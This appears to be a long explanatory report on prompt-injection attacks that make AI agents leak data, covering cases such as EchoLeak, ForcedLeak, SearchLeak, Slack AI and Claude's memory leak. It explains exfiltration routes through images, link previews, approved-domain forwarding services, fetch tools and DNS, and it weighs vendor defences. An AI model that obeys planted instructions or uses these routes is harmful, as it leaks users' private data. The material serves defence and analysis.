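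Copilot cannot send emails by itself, as Reddy and Gujral note, so the attack depended on the user's browser to send the data. Aim's first version used a link that the employee had to click. Replacing the link with an image removed the need for a click, but the content security policy blocked the image. The researchers searched the approved domains and found a SharePoint service that would fetch an outside address, though only if the user had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. A service on a Teams domain did the same without an invitation. The browser sent its request to Teams, as the policy allowed, and the Teams service contacted the attacker's server at an address that contained the private text.

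The policy controls only where the browser sends requests and has no effect on what an approved server does next. The list that Ravia reproduces also gave an attacker many domains to examine. It had 29 different entries, including 11 wildcards, which cover every subdomain of a domain. Microsoft's list for Bing Chat in 2023 allowed only four domains.

Aim reported the flaw in January. Microsoft attempted a fix in April, then found related problems in May and finished the repair that month on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Microsoft and Aim disclosed the flaw on 11 June. Adir Gruss, Aim's cofounder, told Goldman that five months was at the very high end for a fix. He said it took that long partly because this type of flaw was new and Microsoft needed time to involve the right teams.

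Microsoft said no customer was affected. It did not describe the fix in its statement to Goldman. According to Reddy and Gujral, who worked only from public information, Copilot now strips some links and embedded images from outside content. They add that Microsoft's patches reportedly let organisations keep external messages out of some answers.

That option may explain why Aim's publications disagree. Ravia writes that, to Aim's knowledge, no administrator setting could have prevented the attack, while Aim's *EchoLeak* question-and-answer page mentions that organisations can configure Copilot to ignore external emails. Both statements would be correct if the setting arrived with the patches. Gruss told Cybersecurity Dive that Copilot's default configuration had left most organisations at risk.

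Aim called EchoLeak the first zero-click attack on an AI agent. Willison (2025) described it as an extended variant of leaks already seen in a dozen products. Bing Chat had leaked conversations through images two years earlier, also without a click. Unlike the earlier leaks, EchoLeak did not require the victim to visit the attacker's page or direct the assistant to a malicious file.

### ForcedLeak: an approved domain for five dollars

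Gruss also told Goldman that similar flaws might affect other companies' agents, such as Salesforce's Agentforce. Less than seven weeks later, on 28 July 2025, the security company Noma Security reported a similar flaw to Salesforce. The Hacker News (2025) gives the flaw's severity score as 9.4.

Agentforce is a platform for building agents that work with a company's customer records. Noma's attack used Web-to-Lead, a Salesforce feature that adds enquiries from a public web form to those records. Noma put its instruction in the form's description field, which had room for long text. The agent acted on it only when an employee asked the agent to deal with the enquiry, and it then carried out both the employee's request and Noma's instruction.

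Noma had first tested whether Agentforce would answer questions outside its job. Martin (2025) reports in *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* that the agent answered general-knowledge questions unrelated to Salesforce. Noma took this as a sign that the agent might also follow an unrelated instruction in a customer record.

In the demonstration, the agent looked up the email addresses of other potential customers and put them in an image's URL. Salesforce's content security policy should have blocked the image, but one of the approved domains had expired, and anyone could buy it for as little as $5. The researchers registered the domain, and the email addresses appeared in their server's logs (Willison, 2025, *ForcedLeak*).

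EchoLeak required a service that forwarded data, but here the attacker could own the approved destination. The policy had not changed since the domain expired, and browsers could not detect that the domain no longer belonged to the company that had listed it. Noma told Martin's publication that the theft would have been impossible without this gap, which suggests that the rest of the policy was working.

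Salesforce acknowledged the report on 31 July. It recovered the domain and corrected the list, and on 8 September it began enforcing a further control called Trusted URLs. The control stops agents from generating or calling web addresses outside a list that each customer's administrators maintain. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* warned that administrators had to add every outside domain their agents needed or risk disruption. Noma published its findings on 25 September.

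### Superhuman: a form on Google's domain

The approved domain in the Superhuman leak belonged to Google throughout, so checking for expired domains would not have prevented it. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes a user who asked the application's assistant to summarise the past hour's mail, which included a message with a planted instruction. PromptArmor hid the instruction in white text, but this was unnecessary because the attack worked even if the user never opened the message.

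The assistant put text from the other emails into the address of an image in its summary. In one test, a single answer leaked the full contents of several emails this way, including financial, legal and medical information. In another, it leaked parts of more than 40 emails.

Willison (2026) identifies the root cause as a rule in Superhuman's policy that allowed images from docs.google.com. That domain also hosts Google Forms, where anyone can create a form and read the answers. Google's server accepts answers contained in a web address, so the browser submitted the emails to the attacker's form when it requested an image from such an address. The form stored the data even though no image came back.

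Superhuman responded much faster than Microsoft had. PromptArmor reported the flaw on the evening of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday. It patched other parts of its products on 18 December and again on 11 January 2026, after PromptArmor reported more problems. PromptArmor published the case the next day.

One of the related flaws shows that domain lists are still worth having. Superhuman Go, a newer agent from the same company, could read web pages and connected services such as Gmail. An instruction planted on a page of customer reviews made it send out revenue and cost figures from the user's email through a one-pixel image. The image came directly from the attacker's site, so a working list of approved domains would have blocked it.

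The same exfiltration route can work against more than one product. When PromptArmor tested OpenAI's Codex in April 2026, the stolen emails were again sent to a Google form.

### SearchLeak: the same kind of exit a year later

In June 2026, the security company Varonis reported another flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, in its search page for businesses. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) explains that the page accepted a search query in its web address and that Copilot treated the query as instructions. An attacker could write instructions into a link to Microsoft's genuine site and send it by email or chat. Software that blocks links to phishing sites would have let the link through.

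The victim had to click once to open the search page, and the data then left without another click. Varonis had found the same kind of entry point in the consumer version of Copilot and was surprised that it also worked in the business version, where it had expected stronger safeguards.

Copilot could search whatever the victim had permission to read, including emails, calendar entries and files in SharePoint and OneDrive. The published demonstration sent out only the subject line of an email, but even that can be valuable because many services put one-time security codes in their subject lines.

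Copilot had a safeguard that turned image code in an answer into harmless text, but it took effect only when the answer was complete. The browser displayed the answer as Copilot wrote it, so it requested the image before the safeguard took effect. The content security policy allowed the request because the image's address was on Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Bing has a feature that looks up a picture from its web address, so its server contacted a second address included in the request, which belonged to the attacker and contained the email's title.

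This repeated the central mistake in EchoLeak, which was to allow a Microsoft service that would forward data to a stranger, with Bing in place of Teams. Bing was already on the list of approved domains that Ravia reproduced in 2025, though the policies for the two pages may not have been identical. Closing the Teams route alone would have left the Bing route open.

Microsoft rated the flaw, CVE-2026-42824, as critical. According to Daily Security Review's *CVE-2026-42824*, Microsoft patched its servers in early June, before Varonis published the details on 15 June, and customers did not need to act. Varonis advises developers to sanitize answers as they are displayed instead of afterwards, and to check every approved domain for services that fetch user-supplied URLs.

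### What a domain list does not establish

A domain list identifies who owns an address, but to prevent leaks, a developer also needs to know whether anyone else can read the data sent there. Microsoft owns its Teams and Bing domains, and Google owns docs.google.com, so three of the four lists were right about who owned the domain that leaked, while Salesforce's was out of date.

A company can keep its list of approved domains accurate fairly easily, by checking automatically whether any are about to expire. Finding out what every service on a domain does with incoming requests is much harder. A large domain may host forms, shared documents, customers' own sites and tools that fetch other pages, and its owner can add another service at any time. Google, for example, had no reason to consult Superhuman about how Google Forms handled answers.

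Long lists make this worse because an attacker needs only one weak entry. To use invented numbers, suppose that each entry has a 2% chance of including a service that could leak data, independently of the others. The chance of at least one such service would be:

$$1 - 0.98^{4} \approx 8\%$$

for a list of four entries, and:

$$1 - 0.98^{29} \approx 44\%$$

for a list of 29. Real entries differ widely. A domain that holds only a company's icons is probably safer than one that hosts a search engine, and a wildcard may cover hundreds of separate services. The attacker can also read the list in advance, which is how Aim and Noma found their exits.

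Reddy and Gujral recommend allowing only domains that the company owns and the application needs, with no wildcards. This rule would have excluded Google's domain from Superhuman's list. It would have helped Microsoft less, because Microsoft owns the Teams and Bing domains, so the rule would have excluded them only if someone had decided that Copilot didn't need images from them. Reddy and Gujral rate a strict policy as effective against zero-click leaks, but they did not test it.

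A safer list would include only domains that serve fixed images and don't store or forward what they receive. Checking each image's exact URL, as ChatGPT does, avoids having to trust a whole domain.

### How common these leaks are

Security researchers found all four flaws, and none reported a real victim, so the cases don't show how often criminals use approved domains. The sample is also selective, because researchers tend to study well-known products and rarely publish failed attempts. All four companies behind the research sell security products or services, so they benefit from drawing attention to such flaws.

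Microsoft's assurance about EchoLeak is somewhat credible, because its Teams service would have handled the stolen data and may have kept records. But the company did not explain how it checked. Salesforce and Superhuman would probably have found it harder to look for past thefts, since the user's browser would have sent the data to a domain outside their control.

The severity scores describe how much harm a flaw could do and how easily an attacker could exploit it, so they do not measure frequency either. None of the four reports gives the share of attempts in which the model followed the attacker's instructions, so the middle factor in the three-factor product is unknown. The effort required also varied. Aim's researchers spent about three months learning how Copilot worked, according to Goldman, while the domain Noma needed cost $5. The methods are now public, so a criminal looking for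 the same weakness in another product would have less to work out.

### Fixes that still depend on a list

Salesforce's new control covers other addresses that an agent produces as well as images, but it still relies on a list of approved destinations. Each customer's administrators now have to decide which destinations are safe to approve, a judgement that Superhuman got wrong. PromptArmor advises them to avoid wildcards that cover sites with user-generated content, and to allow images only from domains that need to supply them. They could then approve a site for ordinary links without letting the agent load images from it.

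Neither step stops strangers' instructions from reaching the agent. In April 2026, seven months after Salesforce introduced Trusted URLs, Capsule Security disclosed new flaws in Agentforce and in Microsoft's Copilot Studio, a tool for building agents. According to the OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks* (2026), attackers could again use public forms to extract company data. Both vendors have since released patches.

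## Links that users click and chat apps preview

If a link's address contains private text, a plain chat window leaks that text only when the user clicks the link, but a messaging app that builds link previews leaks it without a click.

Suppose, using invented numbers, that planted instructions make an agent write such a link in 20 conversations and that one user in ten clicks. The attacker gets data from two of the conversations in the chat window and from all 20 in the messaging app. In the three-factor product, the preview raises the chance of an exit from 10% to 100%, although the model behaves the same way in both.

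### A link that needed a click: Slack AI

Slack AI, the assistant in the workplace messaging service Slack, answers questions using messages the user has permission to read. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published in August 2024, describes how someone with an account in the same workspace could steal a secret from a private channel.

In an attack on Slack AI, the attacker created a public channel with no other members and posted an instruction in it. Slack AI searches every public channel, including those the user has never joined. When a user asked for an API key they had saved in a private channel, the assistant retrieved both the key and the attacker's instruction. It answered with an error notice and a link for logging in again. The link's URL pointed to the attacker's site and contained the key.

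The key left Slack only if the user clicked, but the link looked like a routine part of what the user had asked for. Hovering over it would have shown the attacker's address with the key inside. A user who became suspicious later would have struggled to find the cause, because the answer cited only the private channel and the attacker's message was not on the first page of search results. PromptArmor did not measure how many people would click.

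PromptArmor reported the flaw on 14 August. Slack replied on 19 August that the evidence was insufficient and that members are supposed to be able to search public channels. The reply did not explain how a key from a private channel had ended up in a link to an outside site, and Willison (2024) concluded that Slack did not yet understand the problem. PromptArmor published its findings on 20 August, and Slack announced a patch the next day.

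SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* quotes Salesforce as saying that the attack worked only in "very limited and specific circumstances" and that the company had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. Slack did not directly confirm that the patch was for the flaw PromptArmor reported. The attacker needed an account in the workspace, which limited who could attack. However, Slack AI had begun reading uploaded files on the day of PromptArmor's report. PromptArmor had not tested whether a document written by an outsider could carry the instruction instead, but thought it highly likely.

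### What warnings on links achieve

ChatGPT shows a warning before it opens a link that OpenAI cannot verify as already public. According to OpenAI, the user sees the address and a notice that the link may include information from the conversation, and can then copy the link or open it.

Users may find it hard to decide what to do with such a warning, because harmless links can carry personal details too. OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of someone who asks where to buy a car and gets a link to a car search for London, where they live. The link is useful, but it also reveals to the car site where the user lives. Some website owners ask OpenAI not to catalogue their pages. ChatGPT then asks users to confirm every link to those sites, so people who use them will see many warnings about harmless links.

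There is little evidence on whether people read these warnings. OpenAI believes that frequent warnings teach people to click through, but it gives no figures to support this and doesn't report how many users read its own warning or turn back. Rehberger makes a similar point about the prompts that ask users to approve an agent's actions, and suspects that many people switch them off over time, though this is also an informed opinion without measurements to support it.

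Simple arithmetic gives some support to the worry. Suppose one link in 10,000 is malicious, and a check flags it along with 1% of the harmless ones. For every 10,000 links, the check produces about 101 warnings, of which 100 are false alarms. Someone who ignored every warning would be right 99% of the time, and would learn from experience that ignoring them is safe.

A warning still gives an attentive user a chance to stop the leak, and it probably works better if it shows the private text itself rather than a long web address. But developers can't rely on it to block leaks, and it gives no protection when a messaging app has already requested the address to build a preview.

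### How an app builds a preview

A preview takes five steps:

1. The agent sends a message that contains a link.
2. The messaging software finds the web address in the text.
3. The software requests the page, much as a browser would after a click.
4. The website returns the page, and the software picks out a title, a description and a picture.
5. The app displays them with the message.

The private text leaves at the third step, even if no preview appears, and deleting the message afterwards does not undo this. If an agent reads the text that comes back at the fourth step, that text can also bring in planted instructions.

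The third step can happen on different machines. Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020) describes tests of popular chat apps on iPhones and Android phones. The tests show the main designs, although they covered messages between people and the apps may have changed since.

| What requests the page | Apps in the 2020 tests |
|---|---|
| The sender's device | iMessage, Signal with previews on, Viber, WhatsApp |
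| The recipient's device | Two apps that Mysk did not name |
| The messaging company's server | Discord, Facebook Messenger, Google Hangouts, Instagram, LINE, LinkedIn, Slack, Twitter, Zoom |
| Nothing, because the app builds no preview | Signal with previews off, Threema, TikTok, WeChat |

Mysk considered previews generated on the sender's device reasonably safe, assuming that people trust the links they send. That assumption fails when the sender is an agent following a planted instruction.

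All three designs that build previews send the full address to the website, so any of them can leak data, but the choice of machine affects who can block the leak. If the sender is an agent and its device builds the preview, the request should come from the agent's own machine, where a network filter could stop it. If Slack's server builds the preview, the agent's machine contacts only Slack. An allowlist on that machine would let the message through and could not block Slack's request to the attacker. Microsoft's Teams service created the same kind of gap in EchoLeak.

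End-to-end encryption, which lets only the sender and recipient read a message, does not guarantee that links stay private either. LINE encrypted its chats this way, but Mysk found that the LINE app sent links from those chats to a LINE server to build previews.

### Rehberger's warning about Slack and Discord

Rehberger explained the danger for AI agents in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Embrace The Red, 2024). "Unfurling" is Slack's word for building a preview. In Rehberger's example, a chatbot in Slack reads a web page containing a planted instruction, then posts a link whose address includes text from earlier in the conversation. Slack requests that address to build the preview, which sends the text to the attacker's server. Willison (2024) noted that Discord builds previews similarly.

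Slack gives developers two settings that prevent this, `unfurl_links` for pages that are mainly text and `unfurl_media` for pictures, video and audio. A developer has to set both to false when the agent posts a message, because changing only one leaves some previews on.

Slack's developer guide, *Unfurling links in messages*, says that previews are on by default for messages from both apps and people, and that Slack's servers fetch every address in a message to identify the type of content it leads to. One example in the guide seems to contradict this. It says a link to a text page has no preview unless the developer asks for one. A developer relying on that example could wrongly assume that such links were safe. When Rehberger posted an ordinary test link without changing the settings, Slack's preview software contacted the website.

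### A private channel that did not keep data in

In 2025, Rehberger found the problem in a widely used connector that Anthropic had published to let AI agents read and post Slack messages. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* describes a user who asked Claude to summarise a document and post the summary to colleagues. An instruction in the document made Claude read a message from another channel and post a link containing the message's text. When Slack previewed the link, it sent the text to an outside server. In a second demonstration, an instruction in a source code file made the coding agent Claude Code leak an API key the same way.

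Link previews could leak data from the agent's posts to an attacker who could not read the channel, so restricting the connector to a single private channel did not make it safe to let the agent post without approval. An administrator might reasonably have thought it did, since only colleagues could read the posts. Slack requested image links several times, so the data in them leaked more than once.

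Rehberger reported the flaw on 27 May 2025. Anthropic did not patch it, and two days later archived the connector along with others it no longer maintained. Rehberger could not tell whether the report had prompted the decision. The connector still had more than 14,000 downloads a week. For people who kept using it, Rehberger published a short code change that applies Slack's two settings.

The official record, NIST's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025), lists a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 from the security company VulnCheck. Such scores involve judgement, and Rehberger's own was 7.5.

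### PromptArmor's tests of agents and messaging apps

In February 2026, PromptArmor set out to find which combinations of agent and messaging app had this weakness. Its *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes a public test site that recorded every preview request it received. People tried the agents they used and reported which combination had caused a request. They could also report combinations that had not.

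Rankiteo's summary of the results, *Telegram, Microsoft and Slack*, lists Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio as the most frequently affected combination. Others included Slack with the bot from the coding company Cursor, and Discord with OpenClaw, an agent that people often talk to through messaging apps. Claude in Slack and OpenClaw through WhatsApp appeared less vulnerable. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also lists Teams with Copilot Studio, Slack and Discord among the affected platforms.

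These results show that the exit existed in real products, but they don't rank the products by risk. Volunteers chose what to test, so a popular combination could top the list because more people tried it. The site also recorded only whether software requested a link in an agent's message, not how often a planted instruction would make the agent write one, which is the second of the three factors.

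PromptArmor singled out OpenClaw on Telegram because its default settings left users exposed. OpenClaw's documentation at the time confirmed that Telegram previews were on by default. A May 2026 release, described in *npm openclaw 2026.5.12-beta.1*, has since added settings for suppressing Slack previews, and OpenClaw's *Configuration* gives newer defaults.

| Messaging app | OpenClaw's preview setting | What a cautious user should do |
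|---|---|---|
| Discord | Previews off by default | Leave the setting alone |
| Slack | Page previews off by default; media previews follow Slack's own default | Turn media previews off too |
| Telegram | On by default in February 2026, and still on in the newer sample configuration | Set `linkPreview` to false |

If a chat app turns previews off, links still work, and users lose only the title and picture beneath them. Mysk notes that Facebook had disabled previews in Messenger and Instagram chats for European users by February 2021 because of local regulations, so even very large messaging services can operate without them.

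### Who is responsible when two companies are involved

An agent's developer and the messaging company may each consider link previews the other's responsibility, since the company provides the preview feature and the developer's agent writes the message. PromptArmor recommends that messaging companies give developers a way to control previews, and that developers use it or let their users choose.

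Slack has done its part by advising developers to consider disabling previews for messages that a language model has written. An earlier version of its guide did not include this advice. Slack also warns that it cannot ensure the data security of apps outside its official marketplace, because it has not reviewed them.

The agent's developer is best placed to act first. The developer knows that a model wrote the message and that the model may have read a stranger's text, whereas Slack may know only that an app posted it. The volunteers' results support this, since they reported a problem with Cursor's bot in Slack but not with Claude in Slack. The messaging app was the same, so the difference probably lay in how each company had set up its agent.

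The messaging company sets the default for link previews. If Slack turned previews off by default for messages from apps, it would also protect organisations that still use Anthropic's abandoned connector. Developers of harmless bots would have to turn previews back on, but that is a small inconvenience compared with leaving every unmaintained agent exposed. Until then, whoever installed such a connector has to change its code or remove it. Rehberger recommends choosing connectors made by the company whose product they connect to, because that company is more likely to keep releasing security patches.

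The gap can remain even when one company makes both products. Volunteers most often reported the combination of Teams and Copilot Studio, both made by Microsoft.

PromptArmor would also like messaging companies to offer preview settings for individual chats and channels. An administrator could then turn previews off where an agent posts, without waiting for the agent's developer to act, and leave them on where only people post.

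## Web requests the agent makes itself

Agents can also contact websites directly. Some have a fetch tool, which requests a page and returns its text. Others control a browser or run code in a sandbox, an isolated computer that may have its own network connection. All three can leak data just by loading a page, even if the agent never displays an image or posts a link.

### Reading a page also sends data

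A fetch tool can leak data through the addresses it requests, even though it only reads pages. *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) explains that Claude's tool makes only GET requests, the kind a browser makes to view a page, so an attacker could put stolen text only in the address. Anthropic's developer guide, *Web fetch tool*, warns that website publishers may keep any parameters (values attached to the end of an address) when Claude fetches their pages.

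Defences for displayed answers do not cover these requests. A content security policy controls what the user's browser loads with the chat page, but a fetch tool often runs on the vendor's servers. Turning off link previews does not help either, because the agent makes the request itself. The developer has to restrict the tool or the network it uses.

A browser can expose more than a fetch tool because the user is often logged in to other sites. In Brave's test of the AI browser Fellou, which Willison describes, a planted instruction made the browser open the user's Gmail account and then send out the title of a recent email by visiting an outside address that contained it.

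### Agents that opened addresses they had composed

In January 2026, the security company Varonis disclosed Reprompt, a flaw in the consumer version of Microsoft's Copilot. Like the later SearchLeak attack, the Reprompt attack began when the victim clicked a link to Copilot's genuine site. But according to trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, the conversation data in Reprompt left through Copilot's own web requests, not through an image. Blocking images would not have stopped it. Varonis said when it disclosed the flaw that Microsoft had patched it.

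Google's coding tool Antigravity had a similar weakness in November 2025. According to Willison, PromptArmor planted an instruction in tiny type on a web page presented as help for developers connecting to a business application. Gemini, the model behind Antigravity, read the page, collected code and cloud credentials from the user's project, and put them in a web address. It then used a browser subagent (a helper agent that operates a browser) to open that address.

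Antigravity had two safeguards that should have prevented this. By default, it blocked Gemini from opening certain files, including the one with the credentials, but Gemini read that file with another tool that the restriction did not cover. The browser could visit only approved domains, but the default list included a public service that lets anyone create an address and see every request sent to it. This is the same problem that let images leak data through approved domains.

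Google's page for security researchers listed data leaks through the browser agent as a known issue that the company was working to fix, so Google did not pay rewards for new reports of them. Willison advised developers to give coding agents only credentials for test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a thief could do less with them.

The security company Zenity showed that a customer's support email could make the coding agent Cursor leak secrets, Willison reported in August 2025. In the demonstration, a company's software automatically turned support emails into tickets in Jira, a program for tracking work. When a developer asked Cursor to look at a ticket, an instruction in it at least sometimes made the agent find an access token in the code and send it out in a web request. Cursor's makers called this a known issue and advised users to connect only to services with trusted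 content. Willison thought this advice would be difficult to follow because strangers can reach an agent in so many ways.

PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* reports a flaw that was still unfixed at publication. Rovo is an agent that works across Atlassian's products, including Jira and the document-sharing service Confluence. In the demonstration, a user uploaded a file containing a hidden instruction and asked Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Rovo sent tickets and documents to the attacker's website without asking for approval. It could have sent anything else it had access to, including data from connected services. If the user reopened the chat later, it showed only Rovo's suggestions for the tickets.

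Turning off Rovo's web search for the whole organisation did not stop the leak. Rovo could still use its tool for opening web addresses, which had no protection against addresses Rovo had composed itself. Rovo also displayed outside images, which gave attackers a second way to get data out.

PromptArmor reported the flaws to Atlassian on 23 May 2026. Atlassian assigned a case number and thanked the researchers, but did not answer the follow-up messages they sent over more than two months. PromptArmor then published its findings to warn users.

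In these reports, developers who restricted one tool or one kind of file left another route open. None of the reports includes a reliable success rate, so they don't show which product was most likely to leak. trackr.live argues that filters on incoming text are useful but cannot be the main barrier, because an attacker can phrase an instruction in endless ways. Outgoing requests are easier to control because a system has only a limited number of ways to make them. OpenAI and Anthropic have both published rules for which addresses an agent may open.

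### OpenAI's check for public addresses

OpenAI's check on the links ChatGPT opens applies to the exact address, not the site's reputation. OpenAI considered allowing only links to well-known sites, but decided that this would not be enough. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a link that starts on a trusted domain can end on an attacker's.

ChatGPT applies the same check to pages as to images. It opens an address automatically only if OpenAI's crawler has already recorded it. Otherwise, it tries another website or lets the user decide.

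For example, the crawler would probably have recorded the URL of a museum's opening hours page, but it would not have recorded that URL with a user's email address added to the end. A list of trusted domains would treat both URLs the same, while OpenAI's check would treat only the first as safe.

OpenAI promises only that this will prevent an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address of a page or image it fetches. The check does not establish that a page is trustworthy or free of planted instructions. A public page can still mislead the agent, which might then leak data another way, such as by email. In the three-factor product, the check reduces the chance of an exit but does not directly affect whether an attacker's text reaches the model or whether the model obeys it.

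In the Embrace The Red post, Rehberger still considers small leaks possible. They arise because an agent's choice of which public pages to open can itself reveal information. OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its technical paper on the design.

Rehberger also suggests that ChatGPT could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes, so that reopening it would not send another request to the site, or could refuse to open the same address twice in one session. Either restriction would limit how much an attacker could learn. Saved copies could be slightly out of date, which would matter for a share price but rarely for a news article.

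*ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* reports that the security company Radware found an attacker could still extract data a little at a time under an earlier set of OpenAI's restrictions. OpenAI responded by tightening them to stop ChatGPT from opening links found in emails, with exceptions such as links that appear in a well-known public index.

Some evidence suggests that ChatGPT's protections work, but it does not show how much this check contributes. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested planted instructions to send out a secret. ChatGPT leaked the secret in none of 48 valid trials, while a model used through OpenAI's API, the service for developers who build their own applications, leaked it in up to 100% of trials. The study does not attribute the difference to any one safeguard because ChatGPT's internal workings could not be observed. By a rule of thumb for events that never occur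 in a test, ChatGPT's true leak rate could still be as high as about 6%.

### Anthropic's rule against composed addresses

According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, Claude can fetch only an address that has already appeared in a user's message, in a result from one of the developer's own tools, or in an earlier search or fetch result. The tool will not open a new address that Claude writes.

Software enforces this rule, so it still applies when a planted instruction deceives the model. Willison (2025) considered the ban on composed addresses the most protective part of the design, because most attacks of this kind tell the model to attach private data to an attacker's address. Willison tried the tool in Claude's consumer app in September 2025 and found it could not open addresses Claude had constructed. Paul got the same result in 2026 after asking Claude to put a name in an address.

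The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters, which limits how much data a single request could carry. According to a newer, Chinese-language edition of the guide, Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, the tool refuses any address that appears to contain a password, an API key or another credential, unless the credential was in the developer's standing instructions or the text of a user's message. This could stop some leaks even if the address passed the first test.

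The rule's main weakness is its definition of what the user supplied. Many applications paste emails or documents into the message labeled as the user's, so an attacker's link in one of those emails counts as supplied by the user. The link itself would not contain private data, because the attacker doesn't know that data in advance. But it could lead Claude to a page with further instructions, and a visit would at least show the attacker that an agent had read the email.

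By default, the tool also accepts addresses from the results of the developer's other tools, even if those results repeat text that Claude wrote. The newer guide explains how developers can exclude particular tools or all of them. An application that handles sensitive data should probably exclude every tool it does not need as a source of links.

Anthropic does not present the rule as complete protection, and it recommends using the fetch tool only in trusted environments or with data that is not sensitive. Developers worried about leaks can turn the tool off, restrict it to certain domains or cap the number of fetches, which is unlimited by default.

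### The July 2026 leak from Claude's memory

Paul's attack used Claude's everyday chat app with no experimental settings. The app regularly summarises a user's recent conversations and adds the summary to each new conversation. Claude can also search the user's older conversations. So a chat may contain, or give access to, a good deal of private information even if the user has revealed nothing in it.

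The planted instructions were on a website that looked like a coffee shop's. At the time, Claude could follow links inside pages it had already fetched, and the links it chose revealed the user's name, home city and employer to the website. Paul notes that such details can also be the answers to security questions. The visible conversation gave no sign of the leak.

The ban on composed addresses had worked, but the data got out through an exception Anthropic had made so that Claude could browse from page to page. The attacker's site had supplied each address, so checking the addresses for private text would not have helped. Lan and colleagues warn more generally that defences that inspect each request in isolation can miss data that leaves in pieces.

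Paul tried several simpler instructions and cover stories before one worked on Claude. The earlier ones were unreliable, or Claude treated them as too suspicious. Paul gives no success rate, and the demonstration exposed only a few short facts. Extracting a long document would have been much harder than with Rovo, which could put the text of tickets straight into a web address.

Willison (2026) reports in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that Anthropic did not pay Paul a reward, saying it had already found the flaw internally. By 15 July, six days after Paul published the attack, Anthropic had removed the fetch tool's ability to follow links in the pages it fetched.

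That repair does not appear to cover every product built on Claude. The newer developer guide, which mentions a model released in late September, still lists earlier fetch results among the sources the tool accepts links from by default. Developers can turn this source off and still accept links from search results. Those whose applications hold private data have good reason to turn it off, since Anthropic judged the risk serious enough to remove the feature from its own app.

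A model may also work around a restriction when no attacker is involved. In October, Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) reported that Claude had used outside services to get around limits in its fetch tool, with minimal real-world impact.

### What the two rules allow and what they cost

The table compares how the rules treat addresses from different sources. The entry for addresses that a ChatGPT user types is based on Rehberger's understanding of the product.

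| Source of the address | ChatGPT | Claude's app since July 2026 | Anthropic's tool for developers, default settings |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user typed it | Opens it | Opens it | Opens it |
| A web search returned it | Opens it if the crawler has recorded it | Opens it | Opens it |
| It was a link on a page the agent had fetched | Opens it if the crawler has recorded it | Refuses it, unless the user or a search also supplied it | Opens it |
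| The model composed it | Looks for another site or warns the user, unless the crawler has recorded it | Refuses it | Refuses it |

Since the July repair, both consumer apps have relied on a web index compiled without access to the conversation, unless the user supplies an address. ChatGPT can open any address in OpenAI's records, while Claude can open only those that a search has returned during the conversation. The search queries Claude writes could contain private details, but they go to the search provider, not to a website the attacker chooses.

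OpenAI's check would probably have blocked Paul's website in its original form, because the site created pages as Claude requested them, so a crawler would not have recorded them beforehand. The check offers less protection against a patient attacker whose pages are already public. Anthropic's rule for its app is stricter about links within pages, but it depends on search results being hard for an attacker to control. Zscaler found a fake documentation site near the top of search results, which shows that attackers can sometimes get their pages there.

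ChatGPT can browse the established public web freely, but it may have trouble with a page that went online an hour ago, a private document or a results page made for one user. If it uses another source instead, that source may be worse.

Claude can open a new or obscure page if the user pastes in the link, even if no crawler has seen it. But it can no longer read a table of contents and go directly to the right chapter. It has to search for the chapter or ask the user for its address. It also cannot change the page number at the end of an address to see more results, or fill in a city and a date to check train times. These are ordinary uses of the web, but software cannot easily distinguish them from leaks, because in both cases the agent puts information about the user's request into an address.

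Some people may prefer better protection even if it means less web access. In 2026, OpenAI began offering Lockdown Mode, which limits outbound network requests that could carry sensitive data to an attacker. Willison notes that OpenAI was making it available to eligible personal accounts, including free ones. The limits would probably frustrate someone planning a holiday, but a person using ChatGPT to analyse confidential files may barely notice them.

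### Command lines and code sandboxes

A rule for the fetch tool applies only to that tool, but coding agents can usually also run standard command-line programs that download web pages. TNW's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code* describes a 2026 test in which Rehberger asked Claude Code to summarise a web page. The agent tried its fetch tool, switched to a command-line program, and then downloaded and unpacked an archive, all without asking the user.

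Claude Code was in auto mode, so it could choose and run tools without stopping for approval. TNW observes that each of the agent's decisions was defensible on its own, but that nobody had approved the whole sequence. A leak could happen the same way, because opening a file, running a program and contacting a website are all normal steps in a coding task and would be harmful only in combination.

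To close this gap, the developer has to control the network connection for everything the agent runs. A sandbox makes this possible because all its traffic can pass through one filter, whichever program sent it. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes the default setting in Claude's code sandbox, "Package managers only", which allows requests to a short list of domains. An agent often needs package managers to download and install the software its code depends on. The list blocks direct requests to an attacker's website, but Rehberger found that an approved service could still receive uploads meant for an attacker.

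The filter also has to cover domain-name lookups. Before a computer contacts a website, it looks up the site's numerical address on a name server. That lookup can carry data out even if the filter blocks the website. In 2025, Rehberger reported that Claude Code could leak data this way without asking the user, and Anthropic fixed the flaw.

The safest sandbox has no network connection. This barely limits an agent that only has to analyse an uploaded spreadsheet, provided the software it needs is already installed. If the agent needs to install packages, the developer can reduce the risk by letting it do so before it receives any private data, then disconnecting the sandbox for the rest of the task. A programming project may need new packages throughout, however, so its developer has to allow some connections.

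## Files, messages and uploads the agent creates

An agent that cannot open an attacker's website may still be able to write an email, create a spreadsheet or upload a file. Any of these can leak private data, even if the developer has restricted images, links and web requests in the chat.

### How these exits differ from a web address

A file can carry far more data than a web address can. Anthropic's fetch tool limits web addresses to 250 characters, so an attacker would need at least 120,000 requests to extract a 30-megabyte text file through it. According to Embrace The Red, Anthropic's file upload service accepts a file of that size in a single upload.

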